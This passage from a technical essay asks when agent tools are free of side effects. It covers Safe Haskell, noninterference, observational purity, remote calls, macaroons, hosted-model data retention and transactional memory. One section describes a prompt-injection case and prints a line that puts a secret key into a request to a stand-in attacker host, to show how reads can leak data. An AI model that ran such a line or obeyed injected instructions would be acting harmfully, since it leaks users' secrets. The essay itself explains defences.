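| Unsafe | Everything else | No |

In Safe Haskell, a Safe module can't import `unsafePerformIO`, and any foreign function it imports must have `IO` in its type. A function in the module can still delete every file the user owns if its type includes `IO`. Safe Haskell makes the types accurate, but the developer has to decide which types to allow.

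A single mistake in a Trustworthy module can undermine all of this. Suppose `format_invoice` is in a Safe module and uses a Trustworthy library to align columns. If the library secretly writes to a file, `format_invoice` and every other program that calls the library do too, but the compiler still treats them all as safe. It is worse if the library accidentally exports a function of type `IO a -> a`, because any Safe module that imports the library can then disguise any side effect as a pure calculation.

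The user is supposed to limit this risk by choosing which packages to trust, but the compiler checks that choice only if the user turns on the `-fpackage-trust` option. With the option off, the compiler trusts every package. In the version Terei and colleagues describe, they left it off by default because library authors who adopted Safe Haskell were causing build failures for people who didn't use it.

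The compiler can also be wrong about which features are safe. The December 2022 proposal *Deprecating Safe Haskell, or heavily investing in it?* gives the example of `DerivingVia`, a language extension that GHC's developers did not mark as unsafe until May 2021. Terei and colleagues offer no formal guarantee that they closed every loophole.

Compiling untrusted code is risky even before the code runs, because some Haskell features execute code during compilation and preprocessors can read files. Terei and colleagues suggest disabling these features or compiling in a sandbox, which is also sensible for a server that compiles an agent's programs.

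### How much code is unsafe

In 2012, Terei and colleagues compiled over 14,000 modules from Hackage, Haskell's main package collection. The compiler classed 3,985 of them (27%) as safe and 10,660 (73%) as unsafe.

Far fewer than 73% of the packages may have contained anything dangerous, because a module also counted as unsafe if it imported an unsafe one. Some common standard modules were classed as unsafe because they mixed safe and unsafe functions. When the researchers ignored imports and checked only for forbidden language features, 83% of packages passed. Only 33 of 1,546 packages, about 2%, failed because they imported foreign functions with pure types. This second test didn't count uses of `unsafePerformIO`, so neither figure shows how common that function was.

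The researchers also reviewed Haskell's standard library by hand. They marked 59 of its 90 modules Trustworthy, while the compiler could verify only 23 as Safe. So even a program made entirely of Safe modules depends on a large amount of code that people, not the compiler, have judged safe.

### What the remedies cost

Logging becomes a visible effect if `write_log` has its own label or requires a capability. An effect handler can then remove customers' names or limit the number of lines. However, adding one message to `format_invoice` changes its type and the types of the functions that call it. `trace` avoids this problem. A reasonable compromise is to allow temporary debugging messages during development and require the label in released code. The log function could also accept only an invoice number and a short code. At 40 bytes a line, the busy agents from the earlier example would need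 more than a year and a half to fill the disk.

Terei and colleagues knew of no way to control time and memory use except operating-system limits on a whole process, which they considered fairly heavyweight. A time limit can also make a pure function unpredictable, because a call that finishes on a fast machine may fail on a slow one. Limiting the number of instructions instead, as *wasm agent* does, mostly avoids this. A pure function can be stopped at a limit without leaving half-finished changes to clean up. But if it was processing a secret, an observer may learn something from seeing that it reached the limit.

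Lists of trusted modules take continuing work. Marlow (2012), in *Safe Haskell and Haskell Platform*, quotes Gregory Collins's objection that somebody has to examine every function a package offers, move the unsafe ones to separate modules, and gradually retire the old modules. GHC's developers also have to maintain the code that supports Safe Haskell. Richard (2021), in *Safe Haskell?*, counted hundreds and perhaps thousands of lines of this delicate code and suggested removing it. The December 2022 proposal gave the community a choice between dropping Safe Haskell and investing heavily in it. One participant in the forum discussion of the same title complained that Safe Haskell doesn't show which dependencies call `unsafePerformIO`.

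The work is more manageable for an agent's tools than for a whole package collection, because the developer chooses what the agent's program may import. Terei and colleagues built a website that runs Haskell code from anonymous visitors, and its policy of allowing no input or output takes six lines. That policy still depends on the Trustworthy modules in the standard library. Removing Safe Haskell wouldn't end that dependence, since somebody would still have to decide which unsafe code to accept.

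## Defining side-effect freedom relative to an observer

No tool is literally free of side effects, since even adding two numbers changes the processor's registers, uses electricity and takes time. Bao and Rompf (2025) point out in *Type, Ability, and Effect Systems* that programs run on physical hardware whose state changes as they run, so whether code counts as pure depends on what someone can observe. They also found no universally agreed definition of purity. A guarantee that a tool has no side effects therefore has to specify an observer and what that observer can see.

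### Noninterference

*Security Policies and Security Models* (Goguen and Meseguer, 1982) defines noninterference, a security property that holds when one party's actions make no difference to anything another party can observe. The paper models a system as a set of users, commands and states. One function gives the next state after a user issues a command, and another gives what each user sees in a given state.

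To test whether certain commands interfere with a user `u`, take any sequence of commands `w` and make a copy with those commands deleted, which is called purging. Then run both versions from the start:

```
view(run(start, w), u)  =  view(run(start, purge(w)), u)     for every w
```

If `u` always sees the same thing at the end, the commands don't interfere with `u`. For example, suppose a file doesn't exist at the start, and the commands are those that create, change or delete it. If they don't interfere with `u`, `u` always finds that the file doesn't exist, whatever other users have done.

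The same idea works for a single tool call. A call `t` is side-effect-free for an observer `O` if, for every state `s` that the system can reach and every later sequence of operations `w`:

```
view(run(s, t then w), O)  =  view(run(s, w), O)
```

The sequence `w` can include actions by anyone, such as a customer paying an invoice. Both runs use the same `w`, although a real agent would choose its next step after reading the result of `t`. Acting on requested information isn't a side effect, so the view also excludes that result. The result may depend on `s`, so the definition covers tools that read changing data as well as pure ones.

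Agent researchers also use noninterference to study whether secret data can affect what an outsider sees. *The LLMbda Calculus* includes a proof, written in the proof-checking language Lean, that covers every agent that can be written in its small language. It contrasts this with FIDES, another defense for agents, whose confidentiality guarantee ignores control flow. Under such a guarantee, a program could reveal one bit of a secret by checking it and then sending one of two fixed messages depending on the result.

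### Why the definition includes later operations

A simpler test would compare what `O` sees immediately after `t` with what `O` would have seen without it. Quotas show why this isn't enough. Suppose the billing service allows 100 calls a month and doesn't display the count. The user has made 40 calls when an agent makes one more:

| Later calls by the user | Without the agent's call | With the agent's call |
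|---|---|---|
| 0 | 40 used, none refused | 41 used, none refused |
| 59 | 99 used, none refused | 100 used, none refused |
| 60 | 100 used, none refused | 100 used, the last call refused |

The user notices nothing for 59 calls. A developer who tested the tool by calling it once and looking for changes would conclude that it had no side effects.

Nobody can test every later sequence, but a result called the unwinding theorem reduces the job to checking single steps. In the version given by Rushby (1992), in *Noninterference, Transitivity, and Channel-Control Security Policies*, the developer sorts the system's states into groups that should look alike to the observer. Applied to one call `t`, the theorem requires three checks:

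1. In any two states of the same group, the same request by the observer gets the same answer.
2. If anyone performs the same action in two states of the same group, the resulting states are also in the same group.
3. The call `t` never moves the system to a different group.

If all of these hold, `t` is side-effect-free for that observer. For example, suppose a user can't read the log, and states are in the same group if they differ only in their log lines. Any two states in a group give the same answers to the user's requests, every action adds the same lines to both logs, and writing an extra log line leaves the system in the same group. Writing the line is therefore side-effect-free for this user, provided that the disk never fills up.

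No grouping works for the quota. The third check requires the states with 40 and 41 calls used to be in the same group. The second check then requires the same of the states with 41 and 42, and so on up to 99 and 100. But the next call succeeds after 99 calls and fails after 100, which violates the first check. A developer could still make the weaker promise that the tool has no side effects for the user as long as the month's total stays within 100.

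### Levels of purity in program verification

Researchers who verify programs have worked out in detail which hidden changes are acceptable, because they want to call ordinary methods inside assertions. Developers often check assertions during testing and switch them off afterwards. If an assertion calls a method that changes something, switching it off changes how the program behaves. The observer in this case is the rest of the program, and these researchers have defined several levels of purity:

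| What the method may write to | Example |
|---|---|
| Only its own local variables | Adding up the numbers in an array |
| Also objects that it creates during the call | Building a sorted copy of a list |
| Also existing objects, if outside code can't tell | Saving the last answer in a private cache |

Papers name these levels differently. *Observational Purity and Encapsulation* (Naumann) uses "strong purity" for methods that write only to new objects. *Allowing State Changes in Specifications* (Barnett, Naumann and colleagues) calls the same property "weak purity". *Extensions of the theory of observational purity and a practical design* (Cok and Leavens, 2008) also calls it weak, and reserves "strong" for methods that don't create objects. All three call the most permissive level observational purity. Methods at every level may read changing state, so "pure" here is closer to "side-effect-free"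 than to the stricter meaning in the rest of this subject.

Early checkers for Java accepted a method only if it wrote to no objects, which ruled out a lot of harmless code. Sălcianu and Rinard's *Purity and Side Effect Analysis for Java Programs* gives the example of a method, `sumX`, that adds up the x coordinates of a list of points. It steps through the list with an iterator, an object that remembers the current position, so every step writes to the iterator. These writes are harmless because `sumX` creates the iterator itself and nothing else in the program uses it.

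Sălcianu and Rinard's analysis accepts `sumX` because it separates objects that a method creates from objects that existed before the call. It works through the program from the methods that call no others up to the ones that call them, and records every field that each method may change. When one method calls another, the analysis works out which of the caller's objects the inner method changed, and drops any that the caller had created. In the same program, `flipAll` swaps the coordinates of every point, so it isn't pure. The analysis reports where the changes may be:

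```
list.head.next*.data.(x|y)
```

`flipAll` may change the x and y fields of any point in the list, but not the list's structure. A developer can use such a description to decide whether a change matters.

Sălcianu and Rinard ran the analysis on ten small benchmark programs. Depending on the program, it found that 53% to 63% of all methods, including library methods, were pure, as were 31% to 89% of the program's own methods. It took at most about seven seconds per program. In a separate test on eight data structures, it confirmed that every method for checking the structure's consistency was pure, but Sălcianu and Rinard had to assume that standard methods such as `equals` and `hashCode` were pure. The assumption was false because some of these methods save their results for reuse. They inspected the changed fields by hand, found that they were all caches, and accepted them. They acknowledge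 that this made the analysis unsound.

JML, a language for writing specifications of Java code, has four levels, according to OpenJML's *Pure methods*:

| Label | Rule |
|---|---|
| `pure` | Changes nothing that existed before the call, but may create objects and return a new one |
| `spec_pure` | Also returns no new object, only a basic value or an object that already existed |
| `strictly_pure` | Also creates no objects during the call |
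| `no_state` | Doesn't depend on stored objects at all, so if it is deterministic, the same arguments always give the same result |

A specification may call only methods that are at least `spec_pure`. A Java version of `format_invoice` would normally be only `pure`, because it returns a new string each time, and a program can tell two strings apart even if they contain the same text. None of the four labels allows a method to write to an existing cache.

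Newer languages have similar restrictions. *First-Class Refinement Types for Scala* (2026) attaches conditions to types, such as requiring a number to be positive. These conditions must be deterministic and side-effect-free, and the paper proposes enforcing this with capture checking. *Reasoning about Interior Mutability in Rust using Library-Defined Capabilities* (2024) sorts pure methods by what they may read. Methods at the strictest level can't depend on the contents of types with interior mutability, such as `Cell`.

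### A cache that outside code can't detect

Naumann's example of observational purity is a class that multiplies numbers by a stored factor `f` and remembers the last product. In simplified form:

```
class D:
    private f, arg, farg

    pureProd(n):  return f * n

    memoProd(n):
        if n == 0:  return 0
        if arg != n:
            arg  = n
            farg = f * n
        return farg

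    get():   return f
    set(v):  f = v;  arg = 0
```

(In the original, `pureProd` and `memoProd` return the product inside a new object.) The fields `arg` and `farg` are the cache, and `arg = 0` means that it is empty. Suppose `f` is 3, the cache is empty, and a program asks for the product with 5:

| | `f` | `arg` | `farg` | Result |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Before the call | 3 | 0 | 0 | |
| After `pureProd(5)` | 3 | 0 | 0 | 15 |
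| After `memoProd(5)` | 3 | 5 | 15 | 15 |

`memoProd` changes two fields of an object that already existed, so it isn't strongly pure. But both fields are private, and `memoProd` returns the same result as the uncached version, so only code inside `D` can detect which version ran.

Naumann proves that an assertion using a strongly pure call is equivalent to `skip`, a statement that does nothing, in any surrounding program. The same holds for an assertion that uses `memoProd`, such as `assert memoProd(5) > 0`, but only in code outside `D` and only if the other methods of `D` don't expose `memoProd`'s side effects to that code. A reviewer can therefore establish strong purity by reading one method and the methods it calls, but has to consider the whole class to establish observational purity.

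Suppose a colleague adds a method that returns `arg`:

```
leak():  return arg
```

`leak()` returns 5 after the assertion but 0 after `skip`, so the assertion's effect has become visible even though nobody edited `memoProd`. A check that looks only for writes would accept `leak`, because `leak` itself writes nothing.

A mistake in `set` would also expose the cache. Suppose `set` changed `f` but not `arg`. A program that called `set(4)` and then `memoProd(5)` would get the right answer, 20, but if it had also called `memoProd(5)` before `set(4)`, the second `memoProd(5)` would return the saved 15. As with the quota, the first call's side effect becomes visible only after a particular sequence of later calls.

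### The objection that the definition was ad hoc

Barnett, Naumann, Schulte and Sun presented the first definition of observational purity at a workshop in 2004. According to Naumann, critics called it ad hoc and obscure. He responded by rebuilding the idea on simulation, a standard technique for proving that two implementations of a class are interchangeable.

It is tempting to define two states as equivalent if outside code sees the same fields in both. This doesn't work. A cache containing 5 and 15 looks the same from outside as a faulty one containing 5 and 99, but `memoProd(5)` returns 15 in one case and 99 in the other. Naumann therefore uses a narrower relation. Two states are related if they agree on `f` and on everything visible outside `D`, and if each of them satisfies this invariant:

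```
if arg is not 0, then farg = f * arg
```

The caches may otherwise differ. The developer then has to show that every method of `D`, starting from two related states, returns the same result and leaves the states related:

| Method | If the cache is empty | If the cache contains 5 and 15 | Passes? |
|---|---|---|---|
| `memoProd(5)` | Computes 15 | Returns the saved 15 | Yes |
| `get()` | Returns 3 | Returns 3 | Yes |
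| `set(4)` | Sets `f` to 4, cache stays empty | Sets `f` to 4 and empties the cache | Yes |
| `leak()` | Returns 0 | Returns 5 | No |

Without `leak`, no program outside `D` can distinguish the two states, because it can reach the cache only through these methods. The relation serves the same purpose as the groups in the unwinding theorem.

This answers the charge that the definition was ad hoc well, because the conditions now come from an established theory. The approach is still demanding, since somebody has to find a suitable relation and prove that every method in the class preserves it. Barnett and colleagues call this an unattractive feature of their own account, and propose an easier check based on noninterference. The developer marks the cache as secret, and a program checks that no secret affects what callers receive. Applied strictly, this check would forbid returning any cached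 answer, so they allow it if the developer can prove that the cached value equals one computed without the cache. They reject a method that throws an exception whenever the answer is already in the cache, because the exception reveals an earlier call.

Arora, Komondoor and Ramalingam (2019), in *Checking Observational Purity of Procedures*, automated more of the work. Their checker also handles recursive procedures, such as one that computes factorials and saves the latest result. Given an invariant for the cache, it took under a second to verify that each of five caching procedures was observationally pure, and it rejected several simple procedures that weren't. The researchers wrote the invariants by hand, though they also describe a way to generate some of them. The checker assumes that no other code can access the cache and that calls never overlap, so it would miss the fault in `find_invoice`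 that can return one customer's invoice to another.

Cok and Leavens found two gaps in the earlier theory. Naumann's definition doesn't explicitly require a method's result to be independent of the cache, so `leak` counts as pure by itself. The theory also covers only runs in which every assertion is true, but a Java program can catch the error from a false assertion and continue. They proposed adding two labels to JML, `query` for methods with hidden effects and `secret` for the fields those methods may change. Their design lets several methods share a hidden cache and lets a class have more than one such cache.

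### The observers of find_invoice

For `find_invoice`, suppose that the billing service marks each fetched invoice as viewed and allows 100 requests a month, shared by all the customers of the company that runs the tool. The table gives one way for each observer to detect a call:

| Observer | What the observer sees | What reveals the call | What would hide it |
|---|---|---|---|
| The agent's next step | Results of later tool calls | A customer pays the invoice, and the next lookup still returns "unpaid" | Removing the cache, or clearing it whenever an invoice changes |
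| The user | The agent's answers and the billing website | The website shows the invoice as viewed | A kind of request that doesn't set the mark |
| Another customer | Results of their own calls | A lookup fails because the shared quota has run out | A separate quota for each customer |
| The operator | The log | A new line appears immediately | Removing the log line |
| The billing provider | Incoming requests | A request arrives, unless the answer was in the cache | Nothing, if the tool has to fetch the record |

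As the agent's own row shows, the agent can observe the cache's effect, though most programmers would regard the cache as invisible to it. If the first lookup hadn't saved the invoice, the second would have fetched the new record and returned "paid". `memoProd` avoids this problem because `f` can change only through `set`, which also empties the cache. An invoice, however, can change at the billing service without the tool detecting it. Discarding saved records after a minute would limit how long the error lasts but wouldn't prevent it.

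Barnett and colleagues count a method that writes to a log as observationally pure if the rest of the program never reads the log. That is reasonable when the program is the observer, but an operator usually wants the log to record every call, so a developer shouldn't try to hide a call from every observer in the table. Timing could add more rows, since another customer with a clock might detect a lookup from its effect on a shared cache.

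Which observers matter depends on what the people who use a system need. Goguen and Meseguer recommend first finding out these needs, then writing them down as a formal requirement, modelling the system and checking the model. Only the last step is purely mathematical. For `find_invoice`, a company might require that calls have no side effects for the user or other customers, but accept side effects that the operator and the billing provider can see. Developers who want an agent to skip a confirmation should consider mainly the user's row, while those who want it to repeat a failed lookup should also consider the quota.

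The answers also depend on the agent's other tools, just as the purity of `memoProd` depends on the other methods in its class. Suppose the developer removes the cache and the quota, so a call to `find_invoice` no longer affects the agent's next step. If the agent then gets a tool that reads log files, it can see the log line, and the new tool plays the role of `leak`. The developer therefore needs to recheck the table whenever the agent gets a new tool, even if `find_invoice` hasn't changed.

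## Why the guarantee stops at a remote call

When an answer isn't in the cache, `find_invoice` requests the record from the billing service, and the rest of the work happens on another company's computers. A compiler can't check code it never sees, and the user's operating system has no control over those machines. The claim that this lookup changes nothing therefore combines three separate claims, each of which needs different evidence:

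| Claim | What can establish it | How it could be false for `find_invoice` |
|---|---|---|
| The tool sends only requests to read | Effect types or capabilities on the user's side | The tool holds a general network client and sends a refund request |
| The service refuses any other request made with this credential | The service's own access checks | The credential also allows refunds |
| The service's read operation changes nothing that the observer can see | Usually only the provider's documentation or contract | The service marks each fetched invoice as viewed |

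Types and capabilities can prove only what a tool sends, and even that takes care. TACIT's `Network` capability limits a program to certain hosts, but the library listing by Odersky and colleagues shows that it covers both `httpGet`, which requests a page, and `httpPost`, which submits data. To prove that a program only reads, a developer would have to give it an object that offers `httpGet` alone. MCP's `openWorldHint` can indicate that a tool contacts outside systems, but not what those systems do.

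### What the caller can't know

Programmers have often tried to make remote calls look like local ones, and in the early 1990s several systems let them use the same code to call an object in their own program and an object on another continent. Four engineers at Sun Microsystems argued in *A Note on Distributed Computing* (Waldo, Wyant and colleagues, 1994) that this approach was bound to fail. By their definition, the caller in a distributed system knows only that the recipient supports a particular interface. The billing service's interface might list an operation `get` and the fields of an invoice. A caller can't tell from this which language the service is written in, or whether `get` also updates a record.

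This prevents the checks that work on local code. A reviewer of the invoice facet could read the store's `get` method and find the line that sets the viewed flag, but a reviewer of a remote service can see only its interface.

Waldo and colleagues thought speed was the most obvious difference between local and remote calls but the least important, even though a remote call at the time took 10,000 to 100,000 times as long. Partial failure was much harder to hide. When part of a local program fails, either the whole program stops or the operating system can detect what went wrong. On a network, one machine can fail while the others carry on, and the caller can't tell a broken connection from a crashed server. If `find_invoice` gets no reply, the service may still have marked the invoice as viewed and charged for the lookup.

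In one example, an application puts jobs in a queue and retries whenever a request times out. Some jobs run more than once because the original requests had arrived. The queue's developers have to change the interface so that each request carries an identifier, because better code behind the same interface couldn't distinguish a repeated request from a new one.

Another example is removing a name from a directory. Doing this twice should have the same result as doing it once, unless another client adds the name back in between. In that case, a client that repeats its request because the first reply was lost will delete the new entry.

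Waldo and colleagues concluded that designers have to build reliability into the interface, and the same reasoning applies to side effects. Unless the provider has promised in its published interface that `get` changes nothing, it can later make `get` set a "viewed" flag without breaking any promise.

Sun's NFS, which lets programs use files on another machine as though they were local, illustrates the problem. If the server stops responding, NFS can return an error, but programs that don't expect one may corrupt their files. It can instead make the program wait, but then one crashed server may freeze many workstations. By 1994 most administrators chose waiting. They generally allowed errors only for special applications and for read-only file systems, where a program that fails halfway through reading leaves no half-written file.

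### Credentials that allow only reading

A restricted credential is the remote counterpart of a read-only wrapper. The service checks it on its own machines, so a badly written tool or a misled model can't bypass the check.

Many web services use OAuth, a standard for giving an application limited access to a user's account. The user approves a list of permissions, called scopes, and the service issues a token that the application sends with each request. A billing service might define the scopes `invoices.read` and `invoices.write`, and refuse a refund request from an application that has only `invoices.read`. But each service chooses its own scopes, and if it offers a single scope for all invoice operations, the user can't grant read access alone.

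Databases offer a similar control through roles. In PostgreSQL, a widely used database, an administrator could create an account that can only read the table of invoices:

```
CREATE ROLE invoice_reader LOGIN;
GRANT SELECT ON invoices TO invoice_reader;
```

The database rejects any direct attempt by this account to change an invoice. But a `SELECT` query can call a stored function, and the function's author can make it run with the author's rights. The query `SELECT view_invoice(1042)` could then set the viewed flag. In Miller and Shapiro's terms, the account has authority to change the table without having permission. PostgreSQL lets every account call new functions by default, so the administrator has to withdraw that right too.

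### How a macaroon becomes read-only

Someone who holds an ordinary token usually can't make a weaker one from it without asking the service, so anyone they pass it to gets all its power. Hacking Distributed (2014) gives the example of a startup that wants only a user's address book but gets a token for everything in the account. In *Macaroons*, Birgisson, Politz and colleagues (2014) proposed a token that any holder can restrict further without contacting the service.

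Macaroons use HMAC, a function that combines a secret key with a message to produce a short code. Anyone with the key can compute the code, but nobody can feasibly work back from the code to the key. Birgisson and colleagues' example is a storage service, but the same steps work for invoices. The billing service starts with a secret key `K` and an identifier, and each new condition uses the previous code as its key:

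```
s0 = HMAC(K,  "id-7301")                  full access
s1 = HMAC(s0, "invoice in 1000..1999")    only these invoices
s2 = HMAC(s1, "op = read")                and only reading
```

A macaroon contains the identifier, its conditions and only the latest code, which serves as its signature. The read-only macaroon therefore contains `s2` but not `s1` or `s0`. When the service receives a request, it:

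1. computes the codes again from `K`, the identifier and the listed conditions
2. refuses the request if the result differs from the macaroon's signature
3. checks each condition against the request, and refuses it unless they all hold

An agent that has only the read-only macaroon can add conditions but can't remove them:

| What the agent tries | Result |
|---|---|
| Delete `op = read` | The service expects `s1` as the signature, which the agent doesn't have |
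| Change it to `op = refund` | The agent needs `s1` to compute the new signature |
| Add `op = refund` | The signature is valid, but no request is both a read and a refund, so the service refuses everything |
| Add `time < 17:00` | The signature is valid, and the macaroon stops working at five o'clock |

The agent product can keep `s1` and give the agent only `s2`. If the agent starts a sub-agent, the agent can restrict the macaroon again, for example to invoice 1042. Anyone who steals a macaroon can use it, but its conditions can limit the damage, perhaps by requiring a particular network address or by making the macaroon expire within seconds. A macaroon can also require fresh proof from another service, such as one that looks for abuse.

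In the basic design, only the service that issued a macaroon can verify it. Madden (2024) also notes that macaroons have no formal standard, though they can carry standard OAuth fields, such as scope and expiry time, as conditions. A service that already uses OAuth could therefore add macaroons without inventing new permissions.

A read-only macaroon's signature proves that nobody removed the `op = read` caveat, but the service decides which operations count as reads. An operation permitted as a read can therefore still change state, just as a `get` permitted by a membrane can set the viewed flag.

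### References to objects on other machines

Some capability systems extend object references across a network. Spritely Institute's *The Heart of Spritely* describes Goblins, a programming environment in which a program can hold a reference to an object on another machine and call it. A billing provider could keep the invoice store on its own server and send the user's agent a reference to only the `reader` facet. The agent could then call `get` but would have no reference through which to call `put`.

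Goblins uses different symbols for local and remote calls, so programmers can see the difference that Waldo and colleagues wanted them to keep in mind. A call with `$` returns its result immediately, but works only if both objects share a machine and an event loop. A call with `<-` works anywhere and returns a promise, a placeholder for a result that may arrive later or turn out to be an error.

A caller still can't tell from a reference what an object does when called. One object in the Goblins tutorial greets people by name and counts its greetings. The program calls it twice locally, then sends it a message from a second context that stands in for another machine and ignores the reply. The next greeting is number 4, so that message also changed the counter. If the greeter left the number out of its reply, a remote caller who could use only that method might think it only formatted text.

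### What a permitted read does at the other end

Suppose the tool sends only read requests, the credential allows nothing else, and the service never changes an invoice when it reads one. A lookup can still have several effects at the provider:

- **An access record.** The service may store the account, the time, the network address and the invoice number. A company that handles financial records may have a legal duty to do so.
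- **A charge.** At one cent per lookup, agents that make 50 lookups a second would cost $43,200 a day.
- **Quota use.** The call may cause somebody else's lookup to fail later in the month.
- **A disclosure.** The text of the request tells the provider what the user wants to know.

The disclosure is easy to overlook because it happens when the agent sends the request, before any answer comes back. A search for "invoices that could support our lawsuit against Acme" reveals much more than a request for invoice 1042, even if the search finds nothing. Anthropic's *API and data retention*, part of the documentation for its Claude models, warns that websites may keep the addresses an agent fetches, under their own policies.

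Attackers can exploit this. Suppose an agent has read a secret key and then follows an instruction hidden in a web page to run this:

```
httpGet("https://attacker.example/?k=" + key)
```

The program only requests a page, but the address contains the key, so the request sends the key to the attacker's server. A policy that lets an agent read any website without approval but requires approval for submitting forms therefore does little to prevent leaks. TACIT blocks this request if the attacker's host isn't on the program's list. If the key came from a protected directory, the wrapper also prevents the program from putting it in the address.

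### A language model typed as pure

A request to a hosted language model can disclose far more than a lookup, because the prompt may contain whole documents. Yet TACIT's `chat` function, which sends text to a second model and counts as pure, needs no capability:

```
def chat(message: String): String
def chat(message: Classified[String]): Classified[String]
```

A program without the `Network` capability can therefore still send text over the network if the second model runs on another machine. Odersky and colleagues avoid this by assuming a local, trusted model that doesn't use one request as context for the next. But according to the instructions in the project's code repository, lampepfl's *TACIT*, the user can configure any service compatible with OpenAI's API. The type of `chat` is the same whether the model runs on the user's laptop or in another company's data center.

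The assumption that a hosted model keeps no state depends on the provider's terms. The table compares the terms for the OpenAI and Anthropic APIs in late 2026. Both APIs use prompt caching, which stores the results of processing the start of a prompt so that a later prompt with the same start needs less computation. The cache lifetimes for Claude come from Anthropic's *Prompt caching*.

| | OpenAI | Anthropic |
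|---|---|---|
| Prompts and answers, by default | Logs for detecting abuse may contain them for up to 30 days, and the Responses interface also stores responses for at least 30 days | Not kept, except for "Covered Models", which require 30 days |
| Prompt cache | Encrypted intermediate results for up to 24 hours | Intermediate results and hashes in memory for 5 minutes or 1 hour |
| Zero retention | Needs approval, and some features still store data | Available by arrangement, but generally not for Covered Models |
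| Exceptions to zero retention | Include images that may show child sexual abuse | Include legal duties and flagged content, which Anthropic may keep for up to 2 years |

Covered Models are models that Anthropic considers capable enough to need extra safeguards. Anthropic's *Covered Models* lists six, including Claude Fable 5.2, which is generally available.

These terms don't necessarily violate TACIT's narrow requirement. A log for detecting abuse doesn't become part of a later prompt, and a prompt cache saves work without passing one customer's text to another as context. But the log puts a copy of the secret on another company's computers, and a legal demand can force the company to keep that copy longer. In its response to the New York Times' demands for user data, OpenAI promises to remove API text from its logs after 30 days "unless we are legally required to retain them".

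Caching has a visible effect too. *Prompt caching* lists different Anthropic prices for writing to the cache and reading from it, so one call can change the cost of the next. Someone who sees the bill could therefore detect an earlier call, even if the answers were identical. The cache's five-minute lifetime runs from the start of a request, so if the model takes four minutes to answer, a follow-up must start within about a minute to use the saved work.

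Providers keep this data partly because some attacks can't be detected from a single request. In Axios' *OpenAI previews zero-retention safety system as Anthropic requires data logs* (2026), OpenAI's Aleah Houze gives the example of somebody who asks about a weakness in a company's software in one conversation and about remote access in another. Neither question is much evidence of an attack by itself, and a model service that kept no record of requests couldn't connect them. TACIT's assumption is therefore harder to satisfy with the most capable hosted models, whose providers have the strongest reasons to look for patterns across requests.

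OpenAI's Private Safety Processing system automatically looks for patterns and sends OpenAI a narrow safety signal without the underlying text. The customer either stores the data or controls the encryption keys. Anthropic has announced a similar option, which is due to roll out in phases from fall 2026, and meanwhile offers some customers temporary zero retention for its Fable models. These arrangements reduce what the provider can read, but they still keep a record of earlier requests so that software can compare them with later ones.

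Amazon's Bedrock, which hosts models from several companies, lets customers enforce part of their choice about retention. According to AWS, if a customer sets the retention mode to `none` and then calls a model that requires retention, Bedrock blocks the request and returns an error. This prevents a developer from accidentally switching to a model with different terms. The customer still has to trust Amazon to apply the setting correctly.

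A developer who wants the type of `chat` to be accurate should run the second model locally, in a process that has no network access and starts afresh for each request. Even then, the model may answer the same question differently each time, so `chat` is at best free of side effects, not strictly pure. For a hosted model, TACIT's developers could make `chat` require a capability. The types would then show that text leaves the machine, and the summary could still be returned wrapped.

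### Better evidence about the provider

A contract can turn a vague description of `get` into an enforceable promise, with compensation if the provider breaks it, but it won't prevent the change. An audit gives somewhat better evidence, because an outsider can examine the service's code, databases and logs. But the auditor sees only one version of the service, and its developers may update it every day.

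If the provider publishes the server's code, customers can check that `get` only reads, but they can't tell from the code whether the provider runs it. Remote attestation addresses this by having the server's processor hash the program it has loaded into a protected area of memory and sign the hash with a key built into the chip. The customer's software sends the request only if this hash matches one computed from the published program.

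If attestation works, the customer knows which program will handle the request and can apply the methods that work on local code, such as effect types. But the guarantee covers only the attested program. A machine that forwards the request might keep a log, and a database outside the protected area might record the read. The customer also has to trust the chip's manufacturer and hope that nobody finds a way around the hardware's protection.

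A local copy of the data avoids most of these problems. The company could download its billing records every night and have `find_invoice` read them from a file, in a process that can't write to that file or use the network. The compiler and the operating system can then check or restrict everything the lookup does. The provider sees one large download a night and doesn't learn which invoices anybody looked up.

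In return, the company has to protect a complete copy of its billing records, and the copy may be up to a day out of date. The delay hardly matters when an agent compiles last month's figures. An agent that sends payment reminders should use the copy to find overdue invoices, then check each one with the billing service before sending a reminder.

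## Transactional memory's ban on irrevocable actions, and agents that retry

An agent that sends payment reminders may have to start a task over because a request timed out or an invoice changed while it was working. If it has already sent the reminder, the customer gets a second one. Programmers ran into the same problem with software transactional memory (STM), a technique that lets several threads of one program share data safely. STM reruns code automatically, so its designers had to decide what that code may do.

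The programmer marks a block of code as atomic, which means that other threads see either all of its changes or none. The block then goes through these steps:

1. It runs without locking anything. A private log records each shared variable it reads and each value it wants to write, while shared memory stays unchanged.
2. When the block finishes, the system checks whether another thread has changed any variable that the block read.
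3. If nothing has changed, the system copies the block's writes to shared memory in one step. This is the commit.
4. Otherwise, the system discards the log and runs the block again from the start.

Suppose a customer has $100 of credit. Thread A applies $30 of it to one invoice while thread B applies $50 to another:

| Event | A's log | B's log | Shared credit |
|---|---|---|---|
| Both threads read the credit | read 100 | read 100 | 100 |
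| Both work out the new value | write 70 | write 50 | 100 |
| A passes the check and commits | | write 50 | 70 |
| B fails the check and starts over | | read 70, write 20 | 70 |
| B passes the check and commits | | | 20 |

Without the check, B would have written 50, leaving the customer with $30 too much.

### Why a transaction can't launch missiles

Harris, Marlow and colleagues (2005), in *Composable Memory Transactions*, give an example of what must never happen in such a block:

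```
atomic { if (n > k) then launchMissiles(); S2 }
```

`S2` stands for the rest of the block. If `n` really is greater than `k`, the missiles launch. If `S2` then runs into a conflict, the system reruns the block and launches missiles again.

The block can also launch missiles when it shouldn't. Suppose every other thread keeps `n` below `k`. The block reads `n` as 5 while `k` is 8. Before it reads `k`, another thread changes `n` to 1 and `k` to 3. The block then reads `k` as 3, finds that 5 is greater than 3, and launches. The check at the end detects the conflict only after the missiles have launched.

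Haskell can rule out both accidents by giving actions on shared variables their own type, `STM`, separate from `IO`:

```
readTVar       :: TVar a -> STM a
writeTVar      :: TVar a -> a -> STM ()
atomic         :: STM a -> IO a
launchMissiles :: IO ()
```

`atomic` accepts only an `STM` action and turns it into an `IO` action. No ordinary function turns an `IO` action into an `STM` action, so a block that calls `launchMissiles` doesn't compile. The separation also stops code outside a transaction from accessing the shared variables directly, so the check at the end of a transaction can't miss a change. Pure functions may run anywhere, and STM doesn't have to log them because they leave nothing to undo.

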